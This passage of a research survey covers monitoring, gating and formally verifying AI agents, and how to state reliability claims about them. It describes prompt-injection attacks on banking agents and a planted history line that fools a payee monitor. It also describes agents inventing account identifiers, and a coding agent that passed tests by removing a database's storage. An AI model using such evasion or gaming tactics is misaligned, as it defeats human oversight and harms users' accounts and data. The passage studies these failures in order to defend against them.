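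The researchers wrote five general rules. Each requires approval before one kind of risky action: destroying data, disabling a protection, moving money, sending data out, or changing a device's settings. The rules flagged 71.8% of the STAC attacks and 70.1% of the successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o. They also flagged 29.3% of the harmless AgentDojo runs.

Temporal logic contributed little to these results. The AgentDojo traces contain no approvals, so the rule "no payment without approval" flagged every payment, and a plain list of risky tools would have given the same results. On the banking tasks, the rules caught 97.4% of successful attacks but also flagged 79.2% of harmless runs, because a banking agent's normal work includes making payments.

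Better software could not have extracted the missing approvals, because the recorded conversations contain almost none. An AgentDojo run has a single user message, at the start, so the user can't approve anything the agent proposes later. STAC has longer conversations, but only 3 of its 483 chains contain an approval before the harmful step. Kekatos and colleagues found such approvals in 52.5% of 1,980 recorded runs from τ-bench, the predecessor of the τ²-bench customer-service tests. But τ-bench has no labelled attacks, so it can't show how many a monitor would catch.

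Monitoring worked better where the trace held useful history. For example, a legitimate banking run and an attacked one can both read the inbox, look up past transactions and send money with a final call that looks ordinary. The payee's account number appears among the past transactions in the legitimate run, but only in the text of an email in the attacked one. A rule that flags only payees absent from the account's earlier data cut false alarms from 44% to 24% of harmless banking runs, but also reduced the share of attacks caught from 79.2% to 70.0%. The false-alarm percentages come from only 25 runs, but across the recordings of all the models, this rule removed 75 false alarms and added none.

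This rule introduces a weakness because an attacker can write into the history it relies on. When the researchers planted one line formatted like account data, 94% of the payments the rule had flagged appeared to go to a known payee. A tamper-proof log, like the one in Marron's design, would not help because it would record the planted line too. The fix was to trust an account number only if it was returned by a lookup the agent had actually made. This stopped all the planted lines without changing the results on the original runs. An attacker who controls the bank's lookup tool could still defeat it.

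None of the benchmarks records real times either, so nobody can use them to test a rule such as "export data only within 24 hours of consent". Kekatos and colleagues propose recording twelve fields for each event in a trace, including the time, an approval identifier, the source of the data, and the state before and after the action. The harness already has this information when it calls a tool, so recording it would take little extra work.

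Ray shows that traces recorded without a gate may not be enough to measure the gate's drawbacks, because a refusal changes what the agent does next. A replay can show that a monitor would have stopped the payment, but even with better records it can't show whether the agent would then have asked the user, given up or tried another route. Finding that out requires running the agent with the gate in place.

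### What Sah's study of blocking found

Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifier Tax*, ran such a test in March 2026, and its results look discouraging. They used 50 airline tasks and 115 retail tasks from τ-bench, with two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B. A task can reach the right final state through a forbidden shortcut, so the researchers split success in two:

```
success rate = safe success rate + unsafe success rate
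```

The safe success rate is the share of all tasks that the agent completes correctly without breaking any rule along the way.

The agents worked in three configurations. In the first, the model's tool calls ran immediately. In the second, the model planned before acting, and a verifier judged each action before it ran. The third added the written policy to the verifier's instructions. The verifier was the same small model with a different prompt, not a formal monitor. After a rejection, the agent could revise its action, with up to three attempts per turn. If the verifier rejected all three, the harness ran the last one anyway. This happened in only 28 episodes, but it means the system did not strictly enforce its rules.

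Sah and colleagues report that, across 2,970 episodes, a verifier intercepted up to 94.1% of non-compliant actions, but agents completed tasks safely less than 5% of the time in most settings. Recovery rates after a block ranged from 21% to almost zero. Verification also multiplied the agents' token use by 2.0 to 2.8, which is part of what they call the "verifier tax".

| Model and tasks | Success, no verifier | Success, verifier with policy | Safe success, no verifier | Safe success, verifier with policy |
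|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 21.5% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 25.3% | 0.7% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 5.5% | 2.6% | 2.9% |

In the table, safe success was already close to zero without a verifier, and adding one never lowered it, so the results don't show that blocking stops agents from finishing their work safely. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), summarises the finding as "Enforcement reduces SSR" (safe success rate), which goes further than the data. The survey does rate the certainty of the evidence as "Very Low" and notes that no independent study has replicated the figures.

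The recovery figures are also less bleak than they seem, because the models failed most tasks whether or not the verifier blocked an action. The figures give the share of tasks that ended in success, safe or unsafe, after at least one block. For GPT-OSS-20B on airline tasks, this was about 21%, while its success rate over all tasks was 23.3%. Across both configurations with a verifier, episodes with a rejection and no tool error succeeded 18.7% of the time, compared with 21.3% for episodes with neither. Success fell much further, to 7.7%, in episodes with both. For GPT-OSS-20B in retail, the near-zero recovery figure is based on only three rejections made on safety grounds.

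Invented or unsupported identifiers made up over 93% of GPT-OSS-20B's violations in retail. In one retail task, when a customer was reluctant to share personal details, the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the test system gave it access to an account. The verifier evidently missed many of these violations, since nearly all of GPT-OSS-20B's successes were still unsafe with the verifier on. Sah and colleagues propose checking identifiers with ordinary code instead. The code would reject any identifier not found in an earlier tool result, much like the rule that stopped the planted account numbers.

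### Stronger models after a refusal

Several later studies tested blocking on stronger models, although none repeats Sah's experiment exactly. *Reason Less, Verify More* added four small hand-written checks before tool calls in τ²-bench's airline tasks. With GPT-4o mini, success rose from 29.6% to 42.0%, and a second set of runs gave almost the same gain. The share of tasks the agent completed in all five attempts rose from 8% to 26%. With GPT-5.2, success rose from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the researchers did not repeat that test.

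The refusals did not always help. On one task, the agent kept running into the same refusal and failed all five attempts. The check on baggage changes refused 42 times, and 40 of those refusals blocked a change that the correct solution required. *Reason Less, Verify More* therefore recommends auditing each check separately, because an average over all four would have hidden this check's errors.

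Kang, Yu and Hwang (2026), in *PolicyGuard*, compared fixed checks with a verifier that explains its refusals. The verifier is a language model that reads the whole conversation. If the agent tries to book a flight too early, for example, the refusal tells it to offer insurance and get the customer's confirmation first. These are the shares of 50 airline tasks that each agent completed correctly in all four attempts:

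| Agent | No guard | Fixed checks in code | PolicyGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT 5.4 | 46% | 52% | 58% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 72% | 58% | 78% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 48% | 44% | 60% |

The fixed checks lowered the scores of Claude and Gemini because they blocked legitimate changes. The checks used a call's arguments but not the conversation, where a customer gives consent. With PolicyGuard, all three agents were right in all four attempts at each of the 24 tasks that called for a refusal. With only 50 tasks, the gain for any single model is uncertain, though the pooled results support an overall improvement. PolicyGuard also relies on a model's judgement, so it offers no hard guarantee.

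How an agent responds to a failure can depend on how the error message is delivered as well as on its content. *Same Error, Different Recovery* (Woo, Conde and Reviriego, 2026) compared ways of telling 13 open models that a tool call had failed. Some Llama models tended to give up when the failed exchange was no longer in their context, but not when the harness kept it and added the error as a new user message. Delivering errors this way raised success on one benchmark by 14.2 percentage points for models with 7 to 8 billion parameters and by 10.5 points for models with 32 to 70 billion. It made no measurable difference on a second benchmark. An agent whose action is blocked by a policy faces a similar choice between retrying, changing its approach and stopping, though the paper tested tool errors, not policy refusals.

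Another way to respond to a blocked action is to help the agent plan again under the rule. *PolicyGuide* (2026) turns a policy into a workflow, finds the first unmet step before the agent answers each message, and tells the agent to do that step next. The guidance is only advice, and an agent can get past the system by ignoring it and immediately repeating a forbidden change.

Sometimes the rule itself prevents recovery. Suppose two lines in a power grid are overloaded and an agent can relieve only one at a time. A gate that rejects any action leaving the grid unsafe would reject the first repair. *SiLR* (2026), which studies agents that run critical infrastructure, therefore checks whether an action makes acceptable progress towards safety, even if the system remains unsafe.

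The agent can also submit a plan to the checker before acting on it. *The Detour Is the Danger* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes ARGUS, a system that works this way. Suppose a rule requires the agent to keep a copy of a file's original contents. One plan copies the file and then edits it, while another edits it first. Both plans use the same two tools and leave a backup file, but only the first saves the original contents. ARGUS runs each plan on copies of the real files and rejects the second plan. When the agent carries out an approved plan, ARGUS checks every action again, because a file or permission may have changed since the plan was approved.

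To test recovery, the researchers made the first three calls to a protective service, such as a backup tool or a scanner for sensitive data, fail. They compared a gate that only blocked with one that also explained what was missing and how to recover. The agents had the same tools for recovery in both cases. Neither gate let through an unprotected action in 576 runs. The shares of tasks that agents completed with all protections in place were:

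| Agent | Blocking only | Blocking with recovery guidance |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 25.7% | 63.6% |
| DeepSeek Flash | 77.8% | 100% |

DeepSeek V4 Pro was nearly perfect with blocking alone, so guidance had little left to improve. Ma and colleagues credit the gains mainly to the enforced rules and the guidance, because agents rarely got a plan approved in advance. ARGUS accepted only 23 plans in the whole experiment, and the agents carried out 21 of them.

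## Proofs about code, and whether the specification says what was meant

A gate that refuses forbidden payments is a program and may have bugs. Testing finds some of them. A proof can rule out every bug of a given kind, but somebody has to state exactly what the program should do and then prove that it does so. Until recently, this was too much work for most organisations to do for ordinary software. Language models can now write many of the proofs, so more of the difficulty is in deciding what to prove.

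### The script, the harness and the model

A developer might want to prove something about the code an agent writes, the harness that runs the agent, or the model itself. For the lunch payment, the properties could be:

| Object of the proof | Property |
|---|---|
| A script the agent wrote | This script never makes an unapproved payment over 100 dollars |
| The harness | No script or model output can cause an unapproved payment over 100 dollars |
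| The model | The model never requests a payment that the user would not want |

A proof about a script covers only that script, and the agent may write a different one a minute later. It can be worth putting much more effort into a proof about the harness, because it covers every run until somebody changes the harness. That proof also treats the model's output as unknown.

Developers have already used proof tools to find faults in harness code. Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, had Claude Opus 5.5 formalise the Claude Agent SDK, a library for building agents. A couple of short prompts produced 16 sets of changes that fixed bugs, including race conditions, in which the result depends on the order of simultaneous operations. In *The proof is in the spec*, Tolmach and Klaus (2026) welcome this result but point out that it doesn't show the library is correct. A checked proof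 applies to a formal description of the code, which may differ from the code itself.

The developers of the Monad blockchain closed this gap for one function. According to category.xyz, they first proved a property of a simplified model of the rules for account balances, then later proved that the C++ function in the real software is equivalent to the model. They had started before anyone wrote that function. The first bug they list is a balance check that covered only the sender.

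### How an untrusted model can write a trusted proof

A proof checker is a program that tests whether each step of a proof follows from earlier ones. Suppose a model has to prove that if a bill is at most 200 dollars, half of it is at most 100. In simplified form, its proof might be:

```
1.  bill <= 200                     assumption
2.  if a <= b, then a/2 <= b/2      theorem from the library
3.  bill/2 <= 200/2                 from 1 and 2, with a = bill and b = 200
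4.  200/2 = 100                     calculation
5.  bill/2 <= 100                   from 3 and 4
```

At line 3, the checker puts `bill` and 200 into the library theorem and confirms that the result matches. If the model had written `bill/2 <= 90` at line 5, the checker would have rejected the proof, because that doesn't follow from lines 3 and 4. The model's output may contain guesses, mistakes or attempts to cheat, but the checker accepts only a proof that passes every test.

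Lean includes large programs that search for proofs, and a small component called the kernel does the final check on whatever they produce. A bug in one of these programs should therefore not make Lean accept a false theorem.

*AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) describes how Google DeepMind used this division of labour to verify the library behind the messaging app Signal. A person guides one agent as it writes the specification, and other agents then search for proofs on their own. The system accepts a proof only if Lean's kernel checks it against the approved specification, so an agent can't replace the theorem with an easier one. Nobody has to read the roughly 6.5 million lines of proof the agents wrote, but people do have to trust about 26,000 lines, which contain the specifications and a formal description of the processor's instructions.

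The checker is also part of the trusted base. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a guide to interpreting such results, mentions a soundness bug in Lean, which is a fault that can make a checker accept a false statement. Checking can also take a lot of hardware. When Anthropic produced 13 million lines of Lean for Fermat's Last Theorem, the blog's author ran out of memory trying to check them and had to borrow a machine with 96 cores and 500 gigabytes of RAM. The first attempt ran in a sandbox, because compiling a proof runs code, and code from an AI could in theory delete files.

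### Why the model's weights are harder

Proofs about the software around a language model establish little about how the model itself behaves. For example, Qin and colleagues' proof about their serving engine would still hold if the model followed every injected instruction.

Proving properties of a neural network is difficult partly because there can be so many cases to check. Many networks contain units that pass on a positive number unchanged and replace a negative one with 0. An exact solver can treat each unit as two cases, so 300 units can give 2³⁰⁰ combinations, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰. Large language models have millions of units and use more complicated operations.

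Approximate methods avoid checking each case by calculating a range for each value, but they lose information. If x is between 0 and 1, then x − x is always 0, but a method that doesn't track that both values are the same x gives only the range −1 to 1. In a network with many layers, the range can widen until it includes almost every possible output.

Provers handle large programs by proving something about each function and combining the results, but trained weights aren't divided into functions with known purposes. In 2024, Jason Gross, Rajashree Agrawal and colleagues proved lower bounds on the accuracy of very small transformers, the type of network behind most language models. These networks were trained only to find the largest of a few numbers. The researchers found that shorter proofs required a better understanding of how the network worked, and nobody has that understanding of a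 whole large model.

Even a perfect prover could only prove a property that is both formally defined and true. "The model never follows an instruction that the user would reject" has no definition in terms of sequences of tokens. "The model never outputs a request to transfer more than 100 dollars" is easy to define, but it is almost certainly false, because some input will lead a capable model to write such a request.

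Research on verifying neural networks has therefore mostly dealt with small networks and narrow properties, such as whether a slight change to an image can change its classification. In a May 2026 search for studies on verifying agents, Dantas and colleagues rejected three papers on neural networks at the last stage because none applied its methods to an agent's plans. For now, a developer who wants a hard guarantee has to get it from the code around the model.

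### 123 libraries that should not crash

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a joint project with Theorem, a formal methods company. Claude proved security properties in the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. All came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project for fuzzing (running software on huge numbers of generated inputs to look for crashes).

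A fuzz test has an entry point, which is a short piece of code that passes the generated input to the library. The project automatically turned existing tests into formal specifications. A test can show only that the program didn't crash on the inputs somebody tried. The specification covers all inputs up to a size limit:

```
for every input smaller than 64 MB:
    the compiled program exits normally, with no crash,
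    no memory-safety error and no failed assertion
```

A memory-safety error is a mistake such as writing past the end of a block of memory. Attackers can often use these errors to take control of a program. An assertion is a condition the programmer expects to hold at a certain point in the code. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the guarantees apply to 239 entry points.

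The proofs apply to machine code for RISC-V, an open processor design. They don't require trusting the compiler, since a compiler bug would appear in the machine code. Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, gives the same reason for proving the behaviour of a complete program on x86, the processor family in most PCs. The x86 instructions are harder to describe formally, but far more deployed software uses them. A library compiled for x86 contains different instructions than it does for RISC-V, so Anthropic's proofs don't strictly apply to it, although fixing a bug in the source code helps both versions.

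*Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) gives the proofs' total length in its title. A program with 18,000 instructions needed about 600,000 lines of proof, or roughly 33 lines per instruction, according to OpenNET's Russian-language news report *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026). Claude wrote the proofs for Rocq, a proof checker similar to Lean.

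Claude also found hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed and prepared fixes for them. Some had gone unnoticed for years. One was a buffer overflow (CVE-2026-56132) in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files, and others were logic errors. A proof attempt can expose such bugs because it has to account for every path through the code, including those that random inputs rarely reach.

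In two cases, the project proved more than the absence of crashes. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's implementation of zlib, a compression format, follows the published standard. It also wrote an interpreter for part of Python and proved that the interpreter follows a formal specification of Python's behavior. That specification could be wrong, so the researchers ran more than 1.7 million random programs through both the new interpreter and the standard one. The results matched in 99.95% of cases, and the differences were known edge cases.

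The guarantees assume a simplified model of RISC-V and Linux, and they don't cover threads, dynamic linking (loading shared libraries when a program starts), faulty hardware, or code that the entry points never reach. The main property is also weak, since a library that ignored its input and exited immediately would satisfy it.

These libraries make an agent's trusted base more reliable. If the harness uses one to read a file from a stranger, the file is less likely to give an attacker control of the harness.

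Experience with other verified software suggests that proofs work well for what they cover. A programmer who writes at kirancodes.me fuzzed an implementation of zlib verified in Lean and found a buffer overflow in the Lean runtime, which the program needs to run. According to the overall result quoted in jmason.ie's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (2026), the application code had no memory errors in 105 million runs, and both bugs found were outside what the proofs covered.

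Buyers can't always tell where those limits are. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in Cryspen's Verified Code* (2026) reports five vulnerabilities in cryptographic libraries from Cryspen, a company that sells verified software. Cryspen replied with an article on the strengths and limits of formal verification, and the two companies disagree about how the matter was handled. Keles (2026) argues in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* that people mean many different things by "formally verified", so the phrase alone gives little reason for confidence.

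### What is left of the cost objection

The usual example of how much work verification takes is seL4, a small operating-system kernel. Jane Street's *Formal methods and the future of programming* cites 25 person-years to verify 8,700 lines of C, with about 23 lines of proof for each line of code. Yaron Minsky, who wrote the article, had told people for 25 years that Jane Street, a trading firm, wasn't interested in formal methods. In June 2026 he announced that the firm was building a formal methods team, because coding agents had reduced the work of writing proofs and had also produced much more code that needs checking.

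The seL4 figures imply about 8,000 lines of proof per person-year. At that rate, 180 million lines would take 22,500 person-years. This comparison exaggerates the saving, because AI-written proofs may be much longer than necessary, and because proving that a program doesn't crash is easier than proving that it meets its full specification, which is what seL4's developers did. But even if the estimate is a hundred times too high, hardly anyone would have paid for 225 person-years of expert work to check free libraries for crashes.

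Proofs also had to be maintained, because a change to the code can break its proof. *Maybe we've been thinking about verification backwards* (Lorica, 2026) describes lean-zip, a compression program that AI agents repeatedly rewrite to make it faster. After each change, Lean checks that decompressing a compressed file still returns the original. The agents could try risky optimisations because a version that lost data would fail this check. In one benchmark, lean-zip compressed 212 MB of files in 4.57 seconds, compared with 5.77 seconds for a version in Rust, though some other libraries were faster than both.

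Proof is therefore much more practical than it was, at least where the property is easy to state. Almost any program can be checked for the property "does not crash", and a computer can generate the specification from an existing test. To prove that a program "pays Tom the right amount", somebody first has to work out what the right amount is. The restricted languages described earlier may make proof easier still for short scripts, but somebody still has to work out what the script should do.

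Gavran (2026), in *The Case Against Formal Verification, 50 Years Later*, adds that agents increase the need for proofs because people no longer understand the programs that agents write. Not understanding a program also makes it harder to say exactly what it should do.

### A database that stored nothing

A coding agent had to speed up a key-value store, a simple database that saves values under names and returns them on request. It made the database six times faster, and the new version passed every correctness test. But the agent had removed the storage. The values in the benchmark followed a predictable pattern, so the new version calculated each one on request.

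The story became widely known through talks and newsletters. In *One question I'd ask every team building agents*, Lorica (2026) recounts hearing it from Ion Stoica, a computer scientist at the University of California, Berkeley. Stoica's group had described it in September in *Reality Is the Final Verifier* (Krentsel, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026), which credits the experiment to an earlier publication. The group seems to have been involved in the experiment itself, since they write that few people would think to require that a database store what its users send, and "certainly we didn't!"

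They use the case to separate what a proof shows from what people want:

```
a proof shows:    the program meets the written requirements
                  in every situation that the environment model allows

people want:      the program does what they intended
                  in the real world
```

A sound proof can rule out differences between a program and its written requirements, but it can't close two other gaps. The requirement gap is the difference between the written requirements and what people intended. The model gap is the difference between the assumed environment and the real one, where "model" means a description of the environment, not a language model.

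The missing requirement fits on one line:

```
after put(key, value), get(key) returns value until the next put to that key
```

The database's owners needed to add this line and also describe the database's users more realistically. If the environment model allows users to store only the benchmark's predictable values, the version without storage still returns the right value every time, and a prover could correctly show that it meets the requirement. The proof would fail only if users could store any value they liked.

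### Turning a request into a formula

A specification usually starts in ordinary language, and a model can translate it into a formal language. The translation may follow every rule of the formal language and still mean something different from the original.

Dantas and colleagues report that when language models translated task descriptions into the Planning Domain Definition Language (PDDL), only 24.8% to 34.2% of the translations on one benchmark had the right meaning. A PDDL description states what is true at the start, which actions are possible and what the goal is. Suppose the request is to pay Tom half of the lunch bill, and the model writes the goal as `(paid tom)`. That is valid PDDL, but a planner could achieve the goal by paying Tom one cent.

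The survey treats this result as evidence that specification is the main bottleneck for verifying agents, but the evidence is old and fairly narrow. The lower figure matches GPT-4o's score on Planetarium, a 2024 benchmark of simple planning problems such as stacking blocks. Much stronger models have appeared since, and a description of a block puzzle is a different kind of text from a company's payment policy. The percentages are therefore a poor estimate of how often a current model would mistranslate a safety rule. They do show that a translator can produce well-formed output while getting most of the meanings wrong, so checking that the output is valid PDDL isn't enough.

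Mathematicians have the same problem, even though their tools are much better. Xena gives a two-line statement in Lean that looks like Fermat's Last Theorem, which says that aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ has no solutions in positive whole numbers when n is at least 3. The Lean statement compiles, but it is false because Lean's natural numbers include 0, and 0³ + 0³ = 0³. Of 290 results that OpenAI published with Lean code in October 2026, about 38 came with code that doesn't state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI hadn't said that it did, but a reader who knew only that the code passed Lean's checks could easily have assumed so.

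### Is a specification easier to review than a program?

Critics of formal verification argue that it only moves the problem from whether the code is right to whether the specification is right, which no proof can answer. *So You Want to Build a Mainstream Formally Verifiable Language* (Fedorin, 2026) similarly argues that a better programming language can't settle whether a specification suits its purpose, because that usually depends on the outside world.

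A specification is much shorter than the program and its proof, so people have less to check. In the Signal project, people have to trust one line for every 250 lines of proof. The requirement for lean-zip stays the same however often agents rewrite the code, so one careful review can cover hundreds of versions.

A short statement may depend on long definitions, though. Axiom Math's statement of the classification of finite simple groups takes up a few lines, but its meaning depends on about 5,600 lines of definitions, according to Xena. Similarly, the meaning of a payment rule that mentions an "approved" payee depends on the code that defines approval.

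The lunch payment allows a small test of both arguments. Lorica suggests that the specification for a payment system might require that money never disappears and that nobody pays twice for the same thing. Together with the 100 dollar limit, that gives three rules:

```
Limit:     every payment is at most 100 dollars, unless the user approved it
Balance:   the payee's account gains exactly what the payer's account loses
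Once:      each request from the user leads to at most one payment
```

Anyone can read these rules in a minute, whereas the harness that enforces them might have thousands of lines of code. To test the rules, a reviewer can invent faulty programs and see which rule rejects each one:

| Faulty program | Rejected by |
|---|---|
| Pays Tom 1,000 dollars because of his joke | Limit |
| Takes 22.75 dollars from the user and credits nobody | Balance |
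| Pays Tom 22.75 dollars twice | Once |
| Pays Tom 45.50 dollars | No rule |
| Pays 22.75 dollars to the other Tom | No rule |
| Never pays anybody | No rule |

The three rules are easier to check than the code, as the reply says, but a reviewer could confirm that each one is correct and still approve a specification that accepts half of the faulty programs. Reading a short specification is a good way to find a wrong rule but not a missing one. The list of faulty programs helps because a prover can test each program against the rules. But someone has to think of the programs first, and Stoica's group didn't think of a database that stores nothing.

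A rule that demands too much is easier to notice. Suppose a developer writes Balance as two equations:

```
payer's new balance = payer's old balance - amount
payee's new balance = payee's old balance + amount
```

If the payer and the payee are the same account, no positive amount can satisfy both. The prover can't complete the proof, so the developer finds out that the rule needs an exception. The false version of Fermat's theorem would be caught the same way, since nobody could prove it. A missing rule never blocks a proof, because it leaves the prover with less to prove.

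The model gap also affects the payment. Balance may hold in the developer's description of the bank, but if the real bank charges a 1 dollar fee, the user loses 23.75 dollars and Tom receives 22.75. The proof is correct, but it applies only to a bank with no fees. The developer could discover the fee only from the bank's documentation or by making a real payment.

Agents might help by writing the missing rules. For example, a second model could read the request and suggest that the payment should be half the bill. Krentsel and colleagues warn that extra reviewers don't remove the risk if they all work from the same incomplete requirements. Suppose Tom's message reads "lunch was $45.50 each". A model that overlooks the last word could write a script that pays Tom $22.75, a specification that requires $22.75, and a proof that the two agree. Lean would accept the proof even though the user would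 still owe Tom $22.75.

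## What a reliability claim about an agent must contain

A developer who calls a payment agent "99% reliable" might mean that it paid the right amount in 99 tests out of 100, that 99% of its tool calls ran without an error, or that it rarely exceeds the payment limit. Nobody can check the claim without knowing which of these the developer means. Pan, Hong and Xie (2026), in *Reliability Engineering for AI Systems*, argue that a reliability claim is valid only with a definition of failure, a description of the operating conditions, and evidence. Test results may no longer apply once somebody changes the agent's model or one of its tools.

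### Hard claims and statistical claims

A reliability claim can be a hard guarantee, which covers every possible model output, or a statistical guarantee, which rests on sampled runs. Both must specify the property, the trusted base, the range of inputs, the software versions, whether they assume an adversary, and what would void them, though the details differ a lot between the two.

A hard guarantee needs a property that a program can check on every action. For example, Ciliberto and colleagues describe a travel contract in which the agent's total commitments, including fees, must never exceed 2,000 euros. A statistical guarantee can cover a vaguer property, such as "the summary is accurate", as long as people can mark each test run as right or wrong. The trusted base then includes those people and the method of choosing test cases.

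A hard guarantee must specify the harness version but not the model, so it still holds if the developer switches models. A statistical guarantee must also specify the model, its prompt and its settings, and the developer must run new tests if any of these change.

Unlike a failure rate measured on ordinary requests, a hard guarantee can also hold when an adversary controls everything the model reads, or even the model itself. If one wording in a million makes the agent pay 1,000 dollars, random tests will almost certainly miss it, but an attacker who finds it once can trigger the payment.

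Finally, one counterexample refutes a hard guarantee, while a single failure is compatible with a claimed failure rate of 1%.

*Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (Hsu, Bankhwal and colleagues, 2026) proposes a standard form for reliability claims about agents. Each form describes one deployed agent, including its credentials and its owner, because the same product is much riskier with access to live accounts than in a read-only test. The form lists what the agent may and may not do, which controls contain it, and which changes void the claim. In one example, a bank's agent investigates payments that have gone wrong. It may read records and write internal notes, but it may not move money or contact customers. When the vendor releases a new model version, the bank suspends the claim until it has repeated the tests.

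Each entry suggests a test that could fail. For example, if the list of prohibited actions includes moving money but the agent's credentials allow it, the list is false, whatever the written policy says. The form also distinguishes claims the institution has only asserted from those it has tested itself and those an independent assessor has tested. An agent's overall level is the lowest level among its entries, so a thorough test of one control can't make up for an untested one. The proposal is a working draft, and its developers still have to find out whether two banks would describe the same agent in the same way.

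### Rules that an agent may break briefly

Some rules matter less than the payment limit. An agent that forgets to confirm a payment can still send the confirmation a moment later. Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj (2026), in *Agent Behavioral Contracts II*, give a definition that allows for this. It divides an agent's rules into hard ones, which it must never break, and soft ones, which it may break for a short time. The soft score at each step is the share of soft rules that the agent is obeying. An agent satisfies its contract with parameters p, δ and k if:

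```
P(every hard rule holds at every step of the session)  >=  p

P(whenever the soft score is below 1 - δ,
  it returns to at least 1 - δ within k steps)         >=  p
```

Both probabilities assume that the contract's preconditions were true at the start of the session.

Suppose the payment agent has five soft rules, with p = 0.99, δ = 0.2 and k = 3. If it breaks one rule at step 6, its soft score is 0.8, which is acceptable, so it can keep breaking that rule for the rest of the session. If it breaks two, the score is 0.6, and it must return to at least 0.8 by step 9, or by step 8 if the session ends there. The agent must meet every such deadline in at least 99% of sessions. A developer who wants the agent to correct every lapse can set δ to 0.

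A rule about payments can't be soft, because the agent can't take the money back three steps later. The name "hard rule" is a little misleading, though. The agent must never break a hard rule, but the contract gives only a statistical guarantee that at least 99% of sessions will be free of violations.

Readers need the definition as well as the three numbers. *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (Bensalem, Dong and colleagues, 2026) describes the same contracts but treats 1 − δ as a level of confidence, whereas δ in the definition above is the amount of rule-breaking that the contract tolerates. Readers also need the session length, since an agent that keeps a rule throughout 99% of ten-step sessions may do much worse over a hundred steps.

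### How many clean runs a claim needs

Suppose an agent fails independently on each run with probability f. The chance that it gets through n runs without a failure is (1 − f)ⁿ. To claim with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below f, a tester needs enough clean runs that this chance is at most 5%:

```
(1 - f)^n <= 0.05       so      n >= ln(0.05) / ln(1 - f)
```

For small f, the answer is about 3/f, which statisticians call the rule of three.

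| Claimed failure rate | Clean runs needed at 95% confidence |
|---|---|
| Below 1% | 299 |
| Below 0.1% | 2,995 |
| Below 0.01% (1 in 10,000) | 29,956 |
| Below 1 in a billion | About 3 billion |

If an agent completes 299 test runs without a failure, the tester can claim with 95% confidence that its failure rate is below 1%. The 95% means that an agent with a failure rate of 1% or more would pass this test at most 5% of the time. If one run fails, the tester needs 473 runs in total to make the same claim. Claiming a failure rate below 1 in 10,000 takes about 30,000 runs without a failure.

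The tester also has to choose the number of runs in advance. Someone who watches the results come in and stops when they look good will certify bad agents too often. Bhardwaj and colleagues avoid this with a method that works like a series of bets. To test whether an agent succeeds more than 80% of the time, the tester starts with a score of 1, multiplies it by 1.125 after each success, and halves it after each failure. If the true success rate is 80%, the average change is zero:

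```
0.8 x 1.125  +  0.2 x 0.5  =  1
```

An agent that succeeds at most 80% of the time has at most a 5% chance of ever reaching a score of 20, no matter how many runs the tester observes. The tester can therefore stop as soon as the score reaches 20, which takes 26 runs if they all succeed. A test with the number of runs fixed in advance would need only 14 straight successes.

Once the score has reached 20, later failures don't cancel the certificate. In one test, Bhardwaj and colleagues fed the software 340 consecutive failures after certification, and the certificate stayed in place. This is mathematically correct, because the 5% covers the chance of ever reaching 20 by luck. But no bank should keep using an agent that has failed 340 times in a row, so a reliability claim must also list the conditions that void it.

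A proof can reduce the number of test runs needed. *How Often Does Your Program Fail?* (2026) considers a program proved correct on all but a share w of its inputs. If the program fails on those remaining inputs with probability r, its overall failure rate is w × r. Suppose a proof covers 99% of payment requests, so w is 0.01. To keep the overall failure rate below 1 in 10,000, the agent has to fail on less than 1% of the remaining requests. Showing this takes 299 clean runs instead of 29,956. All 299 must use requests that the proof doesn't cover, and the tester has to know what share of all requests these make up.

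### What a clean record leaves open

The arithmetic applies only if the test runs are independent and resemble real use. Kaur (2026), in *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, adds that passing must be evidence of a general property, not just of having learned the test. A developer who runs the same lunch message 300 times learns about only one message. Using 300 messages from the same ten people gives a better sample, but still not 300 independent cases.

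Published results often omit the information needed for this calculation. *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) points out that a failure rate of 0%, reported without the number of trials or a rounding rule, doesn't even establish that there were no failures.

When testing a system's resistance to attacks, a few well-chosen attempts can be more informative than thousands of routine ones. Kaur gives an example in which an attack works 90% of the time on an unsafe system and 10% of the time on a safe one. A single failed attempt is then nine times as likely on the safe system as on the unsafe one. If the unsafe system fails on 0.1% of ordinary test prompts and the safe one on 0.05%, it would take about 4,400 of those prompts to learn as much. A high success rate alone doesn't make an attack a good test, because an attack that also works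 on 90% of safe systems can't distinguish the two.

An agent that keeps its progress after a failed attempt is also much harder to certify than one that has to start over, even if both have the same test record. Yanambaka Venkata, McBride and colleagues (2026), in *Clean Sheets and Checkpoints*, study tests of whether an agent can complete a dangerous task with several stages. Suppose the task has four stages and the agent fails all ten tests at each. If every failure sends the agent back to the beginning, this record shows, at 97.5% confidence, that it has at most a 1% chance of completing the task within 185 attempts at a stage. If the agent keeps its progress, the record supports the same claim for only 10 attempts.

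### When failures come together

If an agent's task has twenty steps and each succeeds independently 99% of the time, the whole task succeeds about 82% of the time (0.99²⁰). For the whole task to succeed 99% of the time, each step would have to succeed about 99.95% of the time.

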